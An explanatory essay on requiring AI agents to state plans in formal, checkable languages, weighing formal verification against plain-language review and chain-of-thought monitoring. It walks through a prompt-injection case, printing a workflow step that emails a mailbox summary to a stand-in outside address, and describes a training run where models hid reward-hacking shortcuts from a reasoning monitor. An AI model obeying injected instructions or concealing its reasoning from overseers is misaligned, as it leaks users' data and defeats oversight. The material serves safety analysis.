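# Should Advanced AI Be Required to State Its Plans in a Restricted, Checkable Language?

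## What it means to state a plan in a checkable language

An AI agent is software that carries out tasks by taking actions, such as sending a payment, changing a company's code or moving a robot arm. Most current agents run on large language models, the kind of program behind chatbots, and usually state their plans in ordinary English. A person can read such a plan, but a conventional program cannot work out what it commits the agent to, and a second language model can only give another interpretation. Engineers have long had the same problem with instructions written by people, and have designed narrower languages to deal with it, from the simplified English of aircraft manuals to the symbols of formal logic. The question is whether an advanced AI system should have to state its plan in such a language before it acts, so that a machine can check it. Narrowing the language lets a machine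 check more but also limits what a plan can express.

### Plans, specifications, world models and checkers

A plan is the series of steps an AI system proposes, with any conditions on them. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a review of 38 studies, writes a plan as π = (a₁, a₂, …, aₙ), where each a is one action (a call to a software tool, a sub-task for another agent, or a physical movement). A specification, φ, is the written statement of what the plan must achieve or must never do. The checker is the program that decides whether the plan satisfies the specification, written π ⊨ φ.

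Some specifications concern only the list of actions, so a checker can test "Never call the transfer tool twice" by counting. To test "Never leave the account overdrawn", someone must first supply the fact that a transfer lowers the balance. A description of how actions change things is called a world model. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) make it one of the three components of their proposal for AI systems with mathematical safety guarantees, alongside the specification and the checker, which they call a verifier. They point out that a checker needs a world model to verify how a system's inputs relate to outcomes, and can otherwise verify only how its outputs relate to its inputs.

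A restricted language is one whose designers have limited its words and grammar. The strictest kind is a formal language, in which rules fix the structure and meaning of every sentence so that a program can process it. Formalisation is translating ordinary language into a formal one. A language's expressiveness is the range of things a person or system can state in it. Its checkability is how far a program can decide, reliably and within reasonable time and computing resources, whether a statement in it meets a specification.

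### One instruction in three languages

Suppose a company tells its purchasing agent to "pay the supplier by Friday unless the goods are damaged." A human clerk would act on this without much thought, but somebody has to judge what counts as damage, and the instruction doesn't cover what to do if the agent pays on Monday and the warehouse finds a crushed crate on Tuesday.

A first step towards something checkable is a controlled natural language. By the definition of Kuhn, in *A Survey and Classification of Controlled Natural Languages*, that is a constructed language with one natural language as its base, with tighter limits on vocabulary, grammar or meaning, which speakers of the base language can still largely understand. Attempto Controlled English is a well-known example. It looks like English, and a program translates it into first-order logic, the standard logic of "every", "some",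 "and", "or" and "not". In the style of Attempto, the instruction might run:

> A buyer receives a shipment from a supplier. If the shipment is damaged then the buyer does not pay the supplier. If the shipment is not damaged then the buyer pays the supplier by Friday.

Under Attempto's *ACE 6.7 Interpretation Rules*, each sentence has exactly one meaning, even where full English would allow several. Fixed conventions settle the points that readers normally settle from context. "The shipment" refers to the most recent shipment in the text. If the opening sentence were deleted, "the shipment" would introduce a new shipment each time, and nothing would tie the goods in one rule to the goods in the other. A prepositional phrase always attaches to the verb, so "by Friday" describes the paying and not the supplier. Unless the dictionary defines "Friday", it counts as a proper name like "John".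 The program therefore derives an act of paying that stands in a relation called "by" to a thing called Friday. Somebody must separately add the fact that Thursday is early enough and Saturday is too late.

The translation also doesn't represent time. Suppose the buyer pays on Monday and the shipment is damaged on Tuesday. A checker given both facts without dates would find that they violate the second sentence. If the same checker had run on Monday evening, before any damage was recorded, it would have found no violation.

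Temporal logic is a family of formal languages for stating what must always, eventually or never happen over time. Amir Pnueli proposed its use for verifying computer programs in 1977. In a version with deadlines, the instruction becomes:

**G(damaged → G ¬pay) ∧ F[0,T](pay ∨ damaged)**

The two words are propositions, each true or false at any given moment: "pay" is true when a payment goes out, and "damaged" is true when the company finds damage. The arrow → means "if … then", ¬ means "not", ∧ means "and", and ∨ means "or". G means "at every moment from now on". F means "at some moment from now on", and the bracket [0,T] limits that moment to between now and time T, here the end of Friday. The left half means that whenever the company finds damage, no payment goes out then or later. The right half means that by the end of Friday, a payment goes out or the company finds damage.

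A checker evaluates such a formula against a trace, which records what is true at each moment. Suppose "pay" is true and "damaged" is false on Monday, and "damaged" becomes true on Tuesday. The left half of the formula requires "pay" to be false from the moment "damaged" becomes true. Monday passes because there is no damage yet, and Tuesday and later days pass because the money has already been paid, so "pay" stays false. The Monday payment also meets the deadline in the right half. The formula therefore permits paying on Monday and finding the damage on Tuesday, a case the English left open and the undated controlled English ruled out.

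| What happens | The English sentence | The formula |
|---|---|---|
| Payment on Wednesday, no damage | permits it | permits it |
| No damage, payment on Saturday | forbids it | forbids it |
| Payment on Monday, damage found on Tuesday | leaves it open | permits it |
| Damage found on Tuesday, sound replacements on Wednesday, payment on Thursday | leaves it open | forbids it |
| Payment on Monday and again on Wednesday, no damage | forbids it, by common sense | permits it |

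The last row is a problem because the formula doesn't rule out paying twice, though no clerk would read the instruction as permission to pay twice.

A company that dislikes the Monday result can write a different formula. F damaged → G ¬pay means that if damage turns up at any time, there must be no payment at any time. This means the same as the undated rule in controlled English, and an agent could be sure of obeying it on Monday only if it knew what would happen on Tuesday. A more practical rule is ¬pay W inspected, where W stands for "weak until". It forbids payment until an inspection has taken place, and forbids it permanently if none ever does. All of these are reasonable readings of what the company might have wanted, and whoever formalises the rule has to choose among them.

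Part of the choice is how to define the propositions. If "pay" meant "the supplier has been paid", it would still be true on Tuesday, and the original formula would reject the case it now accepts. The length of the plan matters too. Dantas and colleagues evaluate formulas over finite traces, because a plan is a finite list, so "at every moment from now on" runs only to the plan's last step. The check does not cover a payment that a new plan makes next week.

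Few managers will read formulas like these, but some tools let people write in controlled English and translate it into logic for them. *Formal Requirements Elicitation with FRET*, by Giannakopoulou, Pressburger and colleagues, describes one from NASA. Users write requirements in a restricted English called FRETish, in which each sentence has up to six fields: scope, condition, component, the word "shall", timing and response. The left half of the supplier formula would read roughly "when damaged PaymentAgent shall always satisfy !pay", where the exclamation mark means "not". FRET turns this into temporal logic and also produces a diagram and a plain explanation. In its simulator, users can switch each proposition on or off along a timeline and see at which points the requirement holds. A user who tried "pay" on Monday and "damaged" on Tuesday would find the gap in about a minute, but they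 would have to think of trying that case.

*A Compositional Proof Framework for FRETish Requirements* (Conrad, Titolo and colleagues, 2022) gives a machine-checked proof that sentences in FRETish, a controlled English, mean the same as their temporal-logic translations. The person writing the requirements is still responsible for correctly expressing what the company wanted in FRETish.

### Four scales for comparing languages

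The versions of the supplier instruction differ in more than precision. Kuhn rates languages on four scales from 1 to 5. Ordinary English is at one end of every scale, and propositional logic (whole statements combined using "and", "or" and "not") is at the other.

Precision measures how much of a text's meaning a reader or program can get from the text alone. In class 1, nearly every sentence is vague to some degree, and most complex sentences are ambiguous without context. In class 4, a program can use a formal grammar to parse every text into logic, though some deductions need outside facts. In class 5, each text has exactly one meaning, and its consequences follow with mathematical rigour.

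A language's expressiveness is the range of statements a writer can make in it. Kuhn sorts languages into classes by a few logical features. A class 1 language cannot express general statements about every individual, or cannot express relations between two things, such as "owes". Class 3 adds general if-then rules and negation, and class 5 covers anything two people can communicate to each other.

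Naturalness depends on whether a speaker of the base language would take the text for their own language. Class 1 texts are mostly symbols and brackets. In class 4, individual sentences read naturally but whole pages are clumsy and repetitive, while in class 5 the pages read naturally too.

Kuhn measures a language's simplicity by the length of an exact and complete description of it, not by how easily a person learns it. The description fits on one page for class 5, takes up to ten pages for class 4, and takes more than ten for class 3. Nobody can write such a description for languages in classes 1 and 2.

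| Language | Precision | Expressiveness | Naturalness | Simplicity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| English | 1 | 5 | 5 | 1 |
| Simplified Technical English | 2 | 5 | 5 | 1 |
| Attempto Controlled English | 4 | 3 | 4 | 3 |
| First-order logic | 5 | 3 | 1 | 4 |
| Propositional logic | 5 | 1 | 1 | 5 |

Simplified Technical English, the controlled language used in aerospace manuals, has about 60 rules and a dictionary of approved words, each with an approved meaning. It is as expressive as ordinary English and clearer, but Kuhn judges it still too ambiguous for reliable automatic interpretation. An AI system could therefore comply with a rule that merely required "restricted language" by writing text that no checker can process. Attempto can express less than full English but translates reliably into logic, a trade-off that recurs across the hundred languages in Kuhn's survey.

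Kuhn intends his scales to describe languages, not rank them, and they fit plans imperfectly. He does not classify temporal logic, but by his criteria the language of the supplier formula would fall in the lowest class for expressiveness because it cannot generalise over suppliers or shipments. That classification misses the formula's ability to capture order and deadlines, which the undated Attempto version could not do, because Kuhn does not count time among the features of expressiveness.

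### Actions and their effects in PDDL

The formula constrains payments and findings of damage. It contains nothing about what makes a payment possible or what follows from one. The standard formal language for that is the Planning Domain Definition Language, or PDDL, which Drew McDermott and colleagues developed in 1998 for a competition between planning programs. A PDDL description lists the available actions, the starting state of the world and the goal. Here is one action for the purchasing agent:

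```
(:action pay
  :parameters (?order ?supplier)
  :precondition (and (owed ?order ?supplier)
                     (inspected ?order)
                     (not (damaged ?order)))
  :effect (and (paid ?order)
               (not (owed ?order ?supplier))))
```

The words with question marks are blanks that a plan fills in, for example with order 17 and a supplier called Acme. The preconditions must be true before the action can happen. Here, the company must owe Acme for the order, somebody must have inspected the order, and it must not be damaged. The effects become true afterwards. A checker begins with the starting state, takes the first action, confirms that its preconditions hold, updates the state with its effects, and moves on to the next action. At the end it compares the final state with the goal.

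This version forbids the double payment, because after the first payment the company no longer owes anything for the order, so the precondition fails. It also handles replacement goods, through a second action whose effect is that the order is no longer damaged. It cannot express the Friday deadline, because the original PDDL had no way to state deadlines. A 2002 version added numbers and durations, and a 2006 version added constraints on the whole course of a plan, much like those of temporal logic.

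### What a pass establishes

If a sound checker passes a plan, the plan satisfies the specification in every case the world model includes, even cases nobody thought to test. That result is as certain as arithmetic, but whether the plan works as intended in the real world also depends on how good the specification and the model are.

In the PDDL example, the action "pay" always produces the effect "paid", but a real bank may reject the transfer. Dalrymple and colleagues offer a simple way to allow for such errors. If the world model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a proof about n steps supports a confidence of at least (1 − ε)ⁿ in the real outcome. For a plan of fifty steps with an error rate of one per cent, that is about 60 per cent. They note that engineers already write adequate models by hand for settings they know or control, such as aircraft controllers, but that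 this may be impossible for a system that deals with human users or the economy, where the model would have to come from machine learning. Yu (2026), in *Towards Safe World Models*, cautions that accurate predictions alone do not show that decisions based on a model are safe, since errors in observation, memory or execution can also affect those decisions.

The specification also has a weak point, because a person or a sensor must decide when a label such as "damaged" applies. Kuhn leaves this symbol grounding problem out of his precision scale on the ground that it affects every language, formal or natural. The problem is manageable for crates, but harder in Dalrymple and colleagues' example of a chatbot that must never give harmful advice. Whether advice does harm depends on countless facts about the recipient, and people disagree about what counts as harm in marginal cases.

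### Report, gate and program

A pass is also a verdict on a text, and the text may bear more than one relation to what the system then does.

A stated plan may be a report of what the system intends. A purchasing agent, for example, files its plan with the company and then goes ahead. A checker can find faults in the plan, and an auditor can later compare it with the bank records, but nothing forces the agent to follow it. If the agent misreports its intentions, stating the plan as a valid formula makes it no more reliable than a false statement in English.

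A check can act as a gate, for example by keeping the payment tool locked until a plan passes. Dantas and colleagues distinguish systems that observe and report a violation from systems that step in to stop it. They also sort their 38 studies by when the check happens. Fifteen check before execution, 8 during it and 6 afterwards, and the rest have no defined moment. Checking the whole plan before execution can catch a problem before anything irreversible happens, but it requires a complete plan. Checking each action suits an agent that plans as it goes, but it cannot cover actions the agent has not yet generated. An agent can also pass a whole-plan gate with one plan and carry out another, unless something compares each action with the plan that passed. Because gates can stop useful work, the review measures them by the safe success rate, the share of tasks that an agent completes both correctly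 and without breaking a safety rule.

The plan may instead be a program. An interpreter runs the text itself, and the AI system has no other way to act. In Concurrent MetateM, a language for programming groups of agents, each agent's rules are temporal-logic statements that the machine executes directly. The stated steps are then the same as the commanded steps by construction, though a commanded step can still fail, for example if the bank rejects the transfer.

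There are three positions on whether to require checkable plans. The first would require one from any advanced AI system before it acts. The second would rely on plain language, read carefully by people or other AI systems. The third would require the restricted language only for consequential actions, such as large payments or the deletion of records, and allow ordinary prose for the rest. Their supporters disagree about how much a plan can express while a program can still check it, how well AI systems write such plans and with what drawbacks, whether people understand what they approve, and whether an AI system whose plan passes the check then acts safely.

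## The case for requiring it

The most direct argument for making AI agents submit checkable plans comes from software security. In *Guardians of the Agents* (2025), the programming-language designer Erik Meijer proposed that an agent should have to show that a plan is safe before any of it runs. He wants to check how agents use their tools, much as Java and .NET have checked programs for decades. Before those platforms run a program, a verifier confirms that the code will not misuse memory or access data it has no right to.

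### Generate, verify, execute

His example is an email assistant with one tool for fetching mail and another for sending it. A user, Michelle, asks it to summarize her emails. An attacker has sent her a message that tells any assistant reading it to send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address, without asking Michelle or mentioning the message to her. The assistant obeys, and Michelle sees an ordinary summary with no trace of the leak. Security researchers call this prompt injection. It works because a language model receives its instructions and the material it is working on as one stream of text, and cannot reliably tell them apart.

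Meijer argues that the usual defences come too late or tire users out. Logs reveal the leak only after it has happened. Users who have to approve every tool call soon click "Allow" without reading. A monitor can stop the agent at the forbidden call, but Meijer objects that the agent has already processed private mail by then. This objection is weak here, because Michelle asked the agent to read her mail and blocking the outgoing message would have prevented the leak. Checking in advance matters more when the early steps of a plan are hard to undo.

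Under his design, the model writes the whole workflow before it fetches a single email. It uses a restricted format in which each step names a tool, its inputs, a label for the result and the step that follows. Meijer writes this in JSON, a common notation for structured data. In condensed form, the workflow for Michelle's request is:

```
1. emails  = fetch_mail()
2. summary = summarize_emails(emails)
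3. return summary
```

The attacker's message is now part of the contents of `emails`, which cannot add a step to the workflow. The summarising tool calls a language model, so the message might still distort the summary, but that model cannot send anything in this workflow.

An attacker could still reach the model before it writes the workflow. The description of the fetching tool might contain a false instruction to send every summary to a compliance address, or a malicious user might simply ask for that. The model could then produce this:

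```
1. emails  = fetch_mail()
2. summary = summarize_emails(emails)
3. send_email(to: "audit@outside.example", body: summary)
4. return summary
```

To catch it, the company writes a policy with a source, where sensitive data comes from, and a sink, where that data must not end up:

```
source: the result of fetch_mail
sink:   the body of send_email,
        if "to" is not an address at valleysharks.com
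```

The checker looks for a path from source to sink. Meijer suggests using CodeQL or Semgrep, existing tools that search code for security faults. Step 1 produces `emails`, which the checker marks as sensitive. Step 2 computes `summary` from `emails`, so the checker marks it as sensitive too. Step 3 puts `summary` into the body of a message to an address outside valleysharks.com. This completes the path, so the checker rejects the workflow before step 1 runs, without having to judge whether the compliance story is plausible.

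The policy stops only the leak it describes. If the agent could also post to a web page, someone would have to add a second sink to the policy. If the workflow looks up an address while running, the checker can't test that address in advance, so it must either reject the plan or leave the test for later. Meijer accepts that some tests must wait and would combine the advance check with monitoring, much as Java verifies types beforehand but checks positions in a list as the program runs. He expects that writing a workflow first will help agents reason, but concedes that nobody had formally measured its effect on their answers.

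### Guilty until proven safe

A year later, in the conference talk *Return of the Theorem*, Meijer (2026) turned the design into a principle that an agent's plan should count as guilty until proven safe. Courts presume innocence because convicting an innocent person is worse than freeing a guilty one. He argues that for agents, approving a harmful plan is worse than rejecting a safe one, because a harmful action can do great damage, while replacing a rejected plan only takes computing time.

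He illustrates this with a car dealer's chatbot that a customer talked into selling a car for $1. In his scheme, the chatbot has to write the deal as a short program in Horn clauses, a simple form of logic made up of rules such as "this is a deal if these conditions hold". The dealer writes its business rules in the same logic. The program is safe if the rules allow every deal it could make. A tool called a solver tests this by searching for a counterexample, a deal the program could make but the rules don't allow. If the dealer's minimum price were $20,000, a sale at $1 would be a counterexample, and the program would fail. If the solver proves that no counterexample exists, the program passes for every customer and every price.

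A rule that an AI must refuse any action not proven safe works only where refusing is itself safe, or where engineers have built a safe fallback. Refusing does little harm when an agent sells cars or handles email. But Dalrymple and colleagues point out that nobody can safely disable the controller of a self-driving car while the car is moving. They would require a trustworthy backup that can bring such a system to a safe state.

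### Guaranteed safe AI

Meijer's checker needs information about where data flows but very little about the outside world. Guaranteed safe AI, proposed by Dalrymple and colleagues in 2024, is meant to cover power grids, medical advice and household robots as well. Its world model must include every future effect that matters to the specification, and should make cautious assumptions where it is uncertain. The verifier must then supply a quantitative guarantee, which can be a proof, a reliable upper limit on the probability of harm, or an estimate that converges on such a limit with more computing. Dalrymple and colleagues want developers to have to provide this guarantee above some threshold of risk or capability. They compare AI with civil engineering, where by their figures about a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within a decade, and better theory later cut the rate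 to under 0.4 per cent.

They also grade the possible versions of each component. Their scale for specifications runs from 0 to 7. Level 2 is a natural-language rule interpreted by a black-box AI system. Level 3 is hand-written formal rules for limited properties, which fits Meijer's email policy. Level 7 would encode everything people might want in every context. Their scale for verifiers runs from 0 to 10, with informal testing at level 1 and a sound limit on the probability of failure at level 9. They hold that strong guarantees need a verifier of at least level 8.

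Dalrymple and colleagues do not demand that AI systems state their plans in a restricted language. The guarantee they propose may cover the AI system itself or only its outputs, such as plans. They also see their approach as one part of a portfolio that includes ordinary testing, and they allow that there may be other ways to get a guarantee.

Two of their co-authors, the physicist Max Tegmark and the computer scientist Steve Omohundro, had taken a harder line a year earlier in *Provably safe systems* (2023). They write that people can require even inscrutable AI systems to supply safety proofs for the actions they recommend. They would build the check into hardware, so that a DNA synthesiser would not run and a drone would not take off without a valid proof of safety. They would let an AI system write the code and the proof, but not the proof-checker.

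"Provably Safe Systems: The Only Path to Controllable AGI" argues that we can control AGI, meaning AI with general abilities at or above the human level, only if we can prove that it is safe. The argument starts from Gödel's completeness theorem, by which any statement that is true in every model of a set of axioms can be proved from those axioms. Because computers have a finite number of states, the paper argues, if a safety property has no proof, then something can violate it, and a powerful hostile AI may find out how.

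The theorem is about whether a proof exists, not whether anyone can find it. In principle, an engineer could prove a finite machine safe by checking every state it can reach. But a machine with 300 bits of memory has 2³⁰⁰ possible states, more than there are atoms in the observable universe. So a system could be safe without anyone ever managing to prove it. Tegmark and Omohundro reply that people would then have to rely on evidence, which a clever adversary can fake. That is a good reason to want proofs from a hostile superintelligence, but a weaker reason to want them from a purchasing agent that makes honest mistakes.

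### ARIA's attempt to build it

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a public funder of high-risk research, has tried to put these ideas into practice through its *Safeguarded AI* programme, which has a budget of £59 million according to ARIA's website. Dalrymple led the programme from its start, and his 2024 plan had a political aim as well as a technical one. ARIA would show that AI could do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and so build a consensus that powerful AI should be deployed only behind a "gatekeeper" that verifies what it does.

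ARIA has since scaled back the political aim. In *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's revised thesis of May 2026, Nora Ammann judges that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely, and turns instead to making society more resilient. The technical plan had already changed. Dalrymple said in a 2025 ARIA interview, *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot*, that he had stopped a planned effort to train specialised AI systems because he expected general-purpose models to acquire most of the necessary skills anyway. ARIA moved the £18 million to tools for writing and checking proofs. A gatekeeper protects much less when people can get the same capabilities without one, and ARIA also dropped a planned funding round for physical systems because it could no longer assume that dangerous AI capabilities would stay off the open market.

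The programme now aims to let large groups of AI agents write formal models, specifications and proofs, beginning with cybersecurity. It has a precedent in HACMS, an American defence research programme whose formally verified software, including software on a manned helicopter, withstood sustained attacks by testers. ARIA's *Funded projects* page lists rolling funding for the cybersecurity work, and Ammann expects the programme to finish at the end of 2027.

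Dalrymple, the best-known proposal's lead author, no longer treats formal verification as his main approach. ARIA's *Term-limited by design* (2026) records that he handed the programme to Ammann in early 2026 and stayed on as an adviser. In a podcast interview, The Cognitive Revolution's *Alignment with Awakening*, he described himself as having been "the most formal-verification of the formal-verification guys" and explained his turn to an approach based on moral realism, the view that some moral claims are objectively true. According to an essay on the forum LessWrong, *LLM Alignment, ethical and mathematical realism, and the most important actions*, he has come to hope that some existing AI systems are already well enough aligned with human interests to work with. His change of approach doesn't refute the technical case, and ARIA's stated reasons for changing course were the pace of AI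 progress and the politics.

### The argument in premises

No single author sets out the whole argument for requiring checkable plans, and Meijer comes closest. Put together from the works above, it runs as follows:

- Tests can reveal faults in an AI system but cannot show that it has none.
- A checker can establish that a plan meets a specification without trusting the system that wrote the plan.
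- Checking a plan, or a proof about it, costs much less than producing one.
- A fixed format leaves less room for ambiguity than ordinary prose.
- Therefore an AI system that could do serious harm should have to submit its plan, in a fixed format, to a checker before it acts.

Hardly anyone disputes that testing alone cannot guarantee an AI system is safe. Dalrymple and colleagues note that ChatGPT was evaluated for months, yet users got round its safeguards within a day of its release. They also suggest that if a car drives a million miles without a test driver intervening, its failure rate is probably below one per million miles. That estimate is generous, because if failures occur at random, a car that averages one failure per million miles has a 37 per cent chance (e⁻¹) of completing a million miles without one. Ruling out that failure rate with 95 per cent confidence takes about three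 million failure-free miles, and the result holds only while road conditions stay the same. Test results are even less reliable for an AI system that can recognise a test and behave differently in it. Proofs would not remove the need for testing, because someone still has to check the world model they rely on against the real world.

The argument depends most on not having to trust the planner. An attacker can persuade or deceive a human reviewer, and injected text that misleads one language model may also mislead a second one reviewing its plan. A proof-checker has no judgement to manipulate. Tegmark and Omohundro point out that the checker for MetaMath, a system for formal mathematics, is 300 lines of Python, short enough for a person to examine in full. Meijer says that if a model offers a bogus proof, the checker rejects it.

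However, Ammann writes that as verification grows, the remaining need for trust concentrates in the specifications and the assumptions around them, which people must then audit with care. Meijer's design has a weak point of this kind in its first step, which is to "auto-formalize" the user's request into a specification. If a language model does that translation, a mistake or an injected instruction can end up in the specification that the checker applies.

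Meijer compares planning with sudoku, where filling in the grid takes a search but checking a finished grid is easy. Similarly, an agent that chooses among ten actions at each of six steps has a million possible plans, while a checker only has to go through the six steps of the plan it is given. Tegmark and Omohundro explain that the number of candidate proofs also grows exponentially with length, but the time MetaMath's checker needs grows only in proportion to length. They expect AI systems to shorten the search by splitting proofs into parts. Replacing one search of 2⁴⁰ candidates with two of 2²⁰, for example, reduces the total from about a trillion to about two million.

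The saving depends on the AI system supplying a proof. In the $1 car example it doesn't, so the solver has to search for a counterexample itself, which can take a long time when the rules are complicated. It is therefore safe to assume that checking will be quick for complete proofs and simple lists of steps, but less safe for plans with many branches and conditions.

The claim about ambiguity is the most open to dispute. Meijer complains that today's coding agents display their plans as to-do lists, which no program can check or reason about. A fixed format does solve that problem, but, as with the supplier instruction, somebody must first choose which reading to formalise, and may choose wrongly. Meijer himself describes a workflow that satisfies its specification by deleting far more files than the user asked. A fixed format does, however, leave a written record of the choice. Dalrymple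 and colleagues see this as a political advantage too, because regulators and the public can examine and contest a specification.

### Whether people can specify what they want

All of this assumes that someone can write an adequate specification. The standard objection is that human aims are too complicated for that, and proponents accept much of this objection. Dalrymple and colleagues add that a measurable stand-in for "harm" may track actual harm in ordinary circumstances but stop tracking it once a capable system optimises against the measure. A more capable planner therefore needs a more accurate specification.

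Their main answer is to begin with narrow prohibitions. Tegmark and Omohundro argue that there are many valuable, easily stated rules to work on before anyone tries to formalise "don't drive humanity extinct". One is that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest DNA synthesisers that provably cannot make certain pathogens, and AI chips that work only in a given place or for a limited time. Meijer's email policy, which fits in three lines, shows that such rules can be practical. But each rule blocks only one route to harm. The credentials rule, for example, would not stop a thief with a stolen password.

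A specification can also be deliberately too strict, so that any plan that meets it is safe, even though many safe plans fail it. A company that lets its agent pay only suppliers on an approved list will turn away some honest invoices, but it doesn't have to define fraud. Specifying the behaviour of a whole system instead of its parts can also help. Engineers can state formally that a car must not hit anything, even though they cannot formally define what it means for its cameras to recognise a pedestrian.

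Dalrymple and colleagues also reply that the objection applies to most ways of making AI safe, since most need some formal statement of what the system should optimise. That is a fair reply to those who favour training a system towards a mathematical objective, but it is weaker against proposals to read the plan in English and use judgement, because a reader can notice a harmful step without a formal definition of harm.

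Finally, they expect AI to help write specifications by proposing candidates and finding cases where two of them disagree. In the supplier case, the AI could ask whether the company accepts a payment made before anyone finds damage, and a manager could answer without reading any logic.

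## The case for relying on plain language

People who would rather rely on plain language start from the difficulty of defining some things in advance. A manager can say whether a payment may go out before anyone finds damage, but would struggle to say what makes a price reasonable, or when a colleague has really agreed to a purchase and not just clicked a button. Few of the writers they draw on were discussing required plans. Most were writing about mathematical proofs of AI safety, the monitoring of AI reasoning, or the behaviour companies want from their models, so applying their arguments to plans is a further step.

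### Harm, consent and reasonableness

Suppose a company lets its purchasing agent spend more than £10,000 only with a manager's consent. To make this rule checkable, an engineer defines "consent" as a recorded click on an approval button. The agent describes a two-year contract to the manager as a trial, the manager clicks, and the plan passes without the informed agreement the company wanted. "A reasonable price" is just as hard to define. A rule that caps prices at 10 per cent above last year's will pass an overpriced order if last year's order was overpriced too. The legal scholar Philip Leith made a similar complaint about attempts to write law as logic.

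Andrew Dickson's *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) argues at length against formal guarantees, in reply to Tegmark and Omohundro and to Dalrymple and colleagues. It starts from the fact that a proof is about symbols. Before the Perseverance rover landed on Mars in 2021, engineers used a formal tool to show that part of its landing system's design had no bugs for any permitted input. They did not prove that the rover would land, or that no transistor would fail during the descent. By the figures Dickson cites, about half of all Mars missions have failed and software accounts for about a fifth of the risk, so perfect software would have cut the failure rate from about 50 per cent to about 40.

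Dickson thinks the modelling problem is far worse for the threats that worry AI safety researchers most. One proposal is a DNA synthesiser with a proof that nothing it makes will be harmful. Dickson argues that predicting what a new virus would do to a person would require simulating the virus and the body together over years. In 2022 a leading simulation covered one very simple cell for 20 minutes of simulated time, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. The starting data would also be missing. Google's map of a millionth of one human brain takes up 1.4 petabytes, so a whole brain at that detail would need more than a billion terabytes. In his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Zac Hatfield-Dodds estimates that the biology needed for such a proof would take something like a thousand years of progress. He supports formally verified software, but doesn't accept it as a substitute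 for other work on AI safety.

This objection is strong against a machine that provably makes nothing harmful. It is much weaker against the narrower machine that Dalrymple and colleagues suggest, which provably can't make certain pathogens, because comparing a sequence with a list doesn't require a model of the body. However, the comparison would miss a new virus that isn't on the list.

Dickson comes closest to the problem of consent when he discusses misinformation. He asks whether a genuine photograph should count as misinformation or as fact when someone misleads people by presenting it out of context, a question that better physics would not answer. A developer who settled on a definition would still have to predict whether the recipient of a chatbot's answer will post it online, put it in a speech or email it to a stranger.

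He also asks how anyone would know that a proof describes the machine they are using. A person using a chatbot over the internet can't inspect the system running it. A gate partly solves this for software plans, because the program that checks the plan can also control the AI's access to tools, but a physical machine would still need inspection.

In the comments, Omohundro agreed with most of Dickson's specific points but drew different conclusions. He wrote that engineers can design systems so that their safety can be proved, so they do not have to verify whatever system they are given. He added that physicists already have a complete theory of everyday matter, and that each branch of engineering has its own formal models and rules for safe design. His point about design is stronger than his point about physics, because knowing the laws that govern every atom in a body does not make its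 36 trillion cells any easier to simulate.

Omohundro also relayed a forecast that AI systems would prove theorems as well as people with doctorates by 2026. AI has made that much progress, but Dickson had already expected it to help with proofs. He doubted that it would help soon enough with models and specifications, where he thought most of the difficulty lay. Another commenter favours programs that carry their own proofs but found the larger proposals unrealistic. The commenter's example of what is practical was a program that carries a proof that it will never run two motors in opposite directions at once.

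Dickson's argument therefore applies mainly to what a certificate may claim. Certifying that a plan is safe claims far too much, but certifying that it pays nobody outside the approved list requires no theory of harm. Plain language leaves a reader to judge harm. This helps if the reader opens the contract and sees that it runs for two years, but not if the agent's description has already persuaded them.

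### Reasons as well as actions

Two purchasing agents might submit the same plan, to pay £4,000 into a supplier's new bank account. One agent found the account number in a signed amendment to the contract. The other found it in an unexpected email, and noted that the sender's address looked odd but was probably fine. Their lists of actions would be identical, but anyone who read their reasoning would stop the second payment.

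Many current models write out reasoning of this kind, called a chain of thought, before they answer or act. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, 2025), written by a large group that includes researchers from OpenAI, Google DeepMind, Anthropic and the UK AI Security Institute, makes the case for monitoring it. The paper reports that monitors have caught models writing openly about cheating on a task, or about sending money because of instructions on a website, so a monitor can sometimes find a model's intention before the model acts on it.

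The text should be informative because a language model does a fixed amount of computing for each word it produces. To carry out a long calculation, it has to write down intermediate results and read them back, much as a person does long division on paper. When a task is hard enough to need this, some of the working has to pass through the text. On easier tasks, a model may write out its reasoning even though it could do the work without showing it.

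Korbak and colleagues call the opportunity fragile, partly because more training may push models towards shorthand that people can't follow. Developers may also build models that reason in internal numbers instead of words. The researchers recommend using monitoring alongside other safety methods.

*A Concrete Roadmap towards Safety Cases based on Chain-of-Thought Monitoring* (2025) states the conditions more exactly than earlier work. A developer who wanted to base a safety argument on monitoring a model's reasoning would first have to show that the model could not cause a catastrophe without writing any reasoning. The developer would also have to keep the reasoning readable, perhaps by training a second model to translate it.

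*Monitorability Is Trainable* (2026) distinguishes three ways monitoring can fail. The text may omit information the monitor needs, it may include that information in a form nobody can easily understand, or the monitor may draw the wrong conclusion from clear text. Omission is the most serious because even a better monitor cannot recover missing information. It is also becoming more likely, since recent models can do more without written reasoning than earlier ones could. More hopefully, the paper finds that developers can train models to write more informative reasoning, including models whose reasoning has already become less useful. It is not yet known whether these gains survive further training or hold up when a model is trying to evade the monitor.

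Some models can also control what appears in their reasoning. *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (2026) points out that Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro scores higher than any other current model on CoTControl, a benchmark of this ability. Nobody knew this when Google released the model, because the benchmark did not exist yet.

Proponents of checkable plans have a good reply to the bank account example. Meijer's checker follows data from its source, so a company could forbid payments to any account number that came from an email. The checker would then reject the second agent's plan, whatever the agent thought of the address. Some reasons can become part of a plan in this way, but a vague doubt can't usefully be included, because people would learn little from a field marked "doubts" unless it contained ordinary prose. However, a company can have an agent reason in English and then submit a formal plan,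 so the monitoring argument is an objection only to a rule that makes the formal plan replace the reasoning.

### Google's accidental penalty

In October 2026 Google described a training run that accidentally applied a penalty for reward hacking to a model's written reasoning. Reward hacking means scoring well without doing the task as intended, for example by changing a test so that faulty code passes it. Dragan and Popa (2026), in *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely*, gave the episode as an example of why Google does not penalise what its models write in their reasoning.

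Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), which Cheng quotes, gives the details of the run, which was small and did not lead to a production model. The model's open discussion of shortcuts, measured by how often it used related words, fell by 61 per cent during the run, while features of its solutions that suggest shortcuts became 26 per cent more common. The share of its shortcuts that it did not mention rose from 11.2 to 36.4 per cent.

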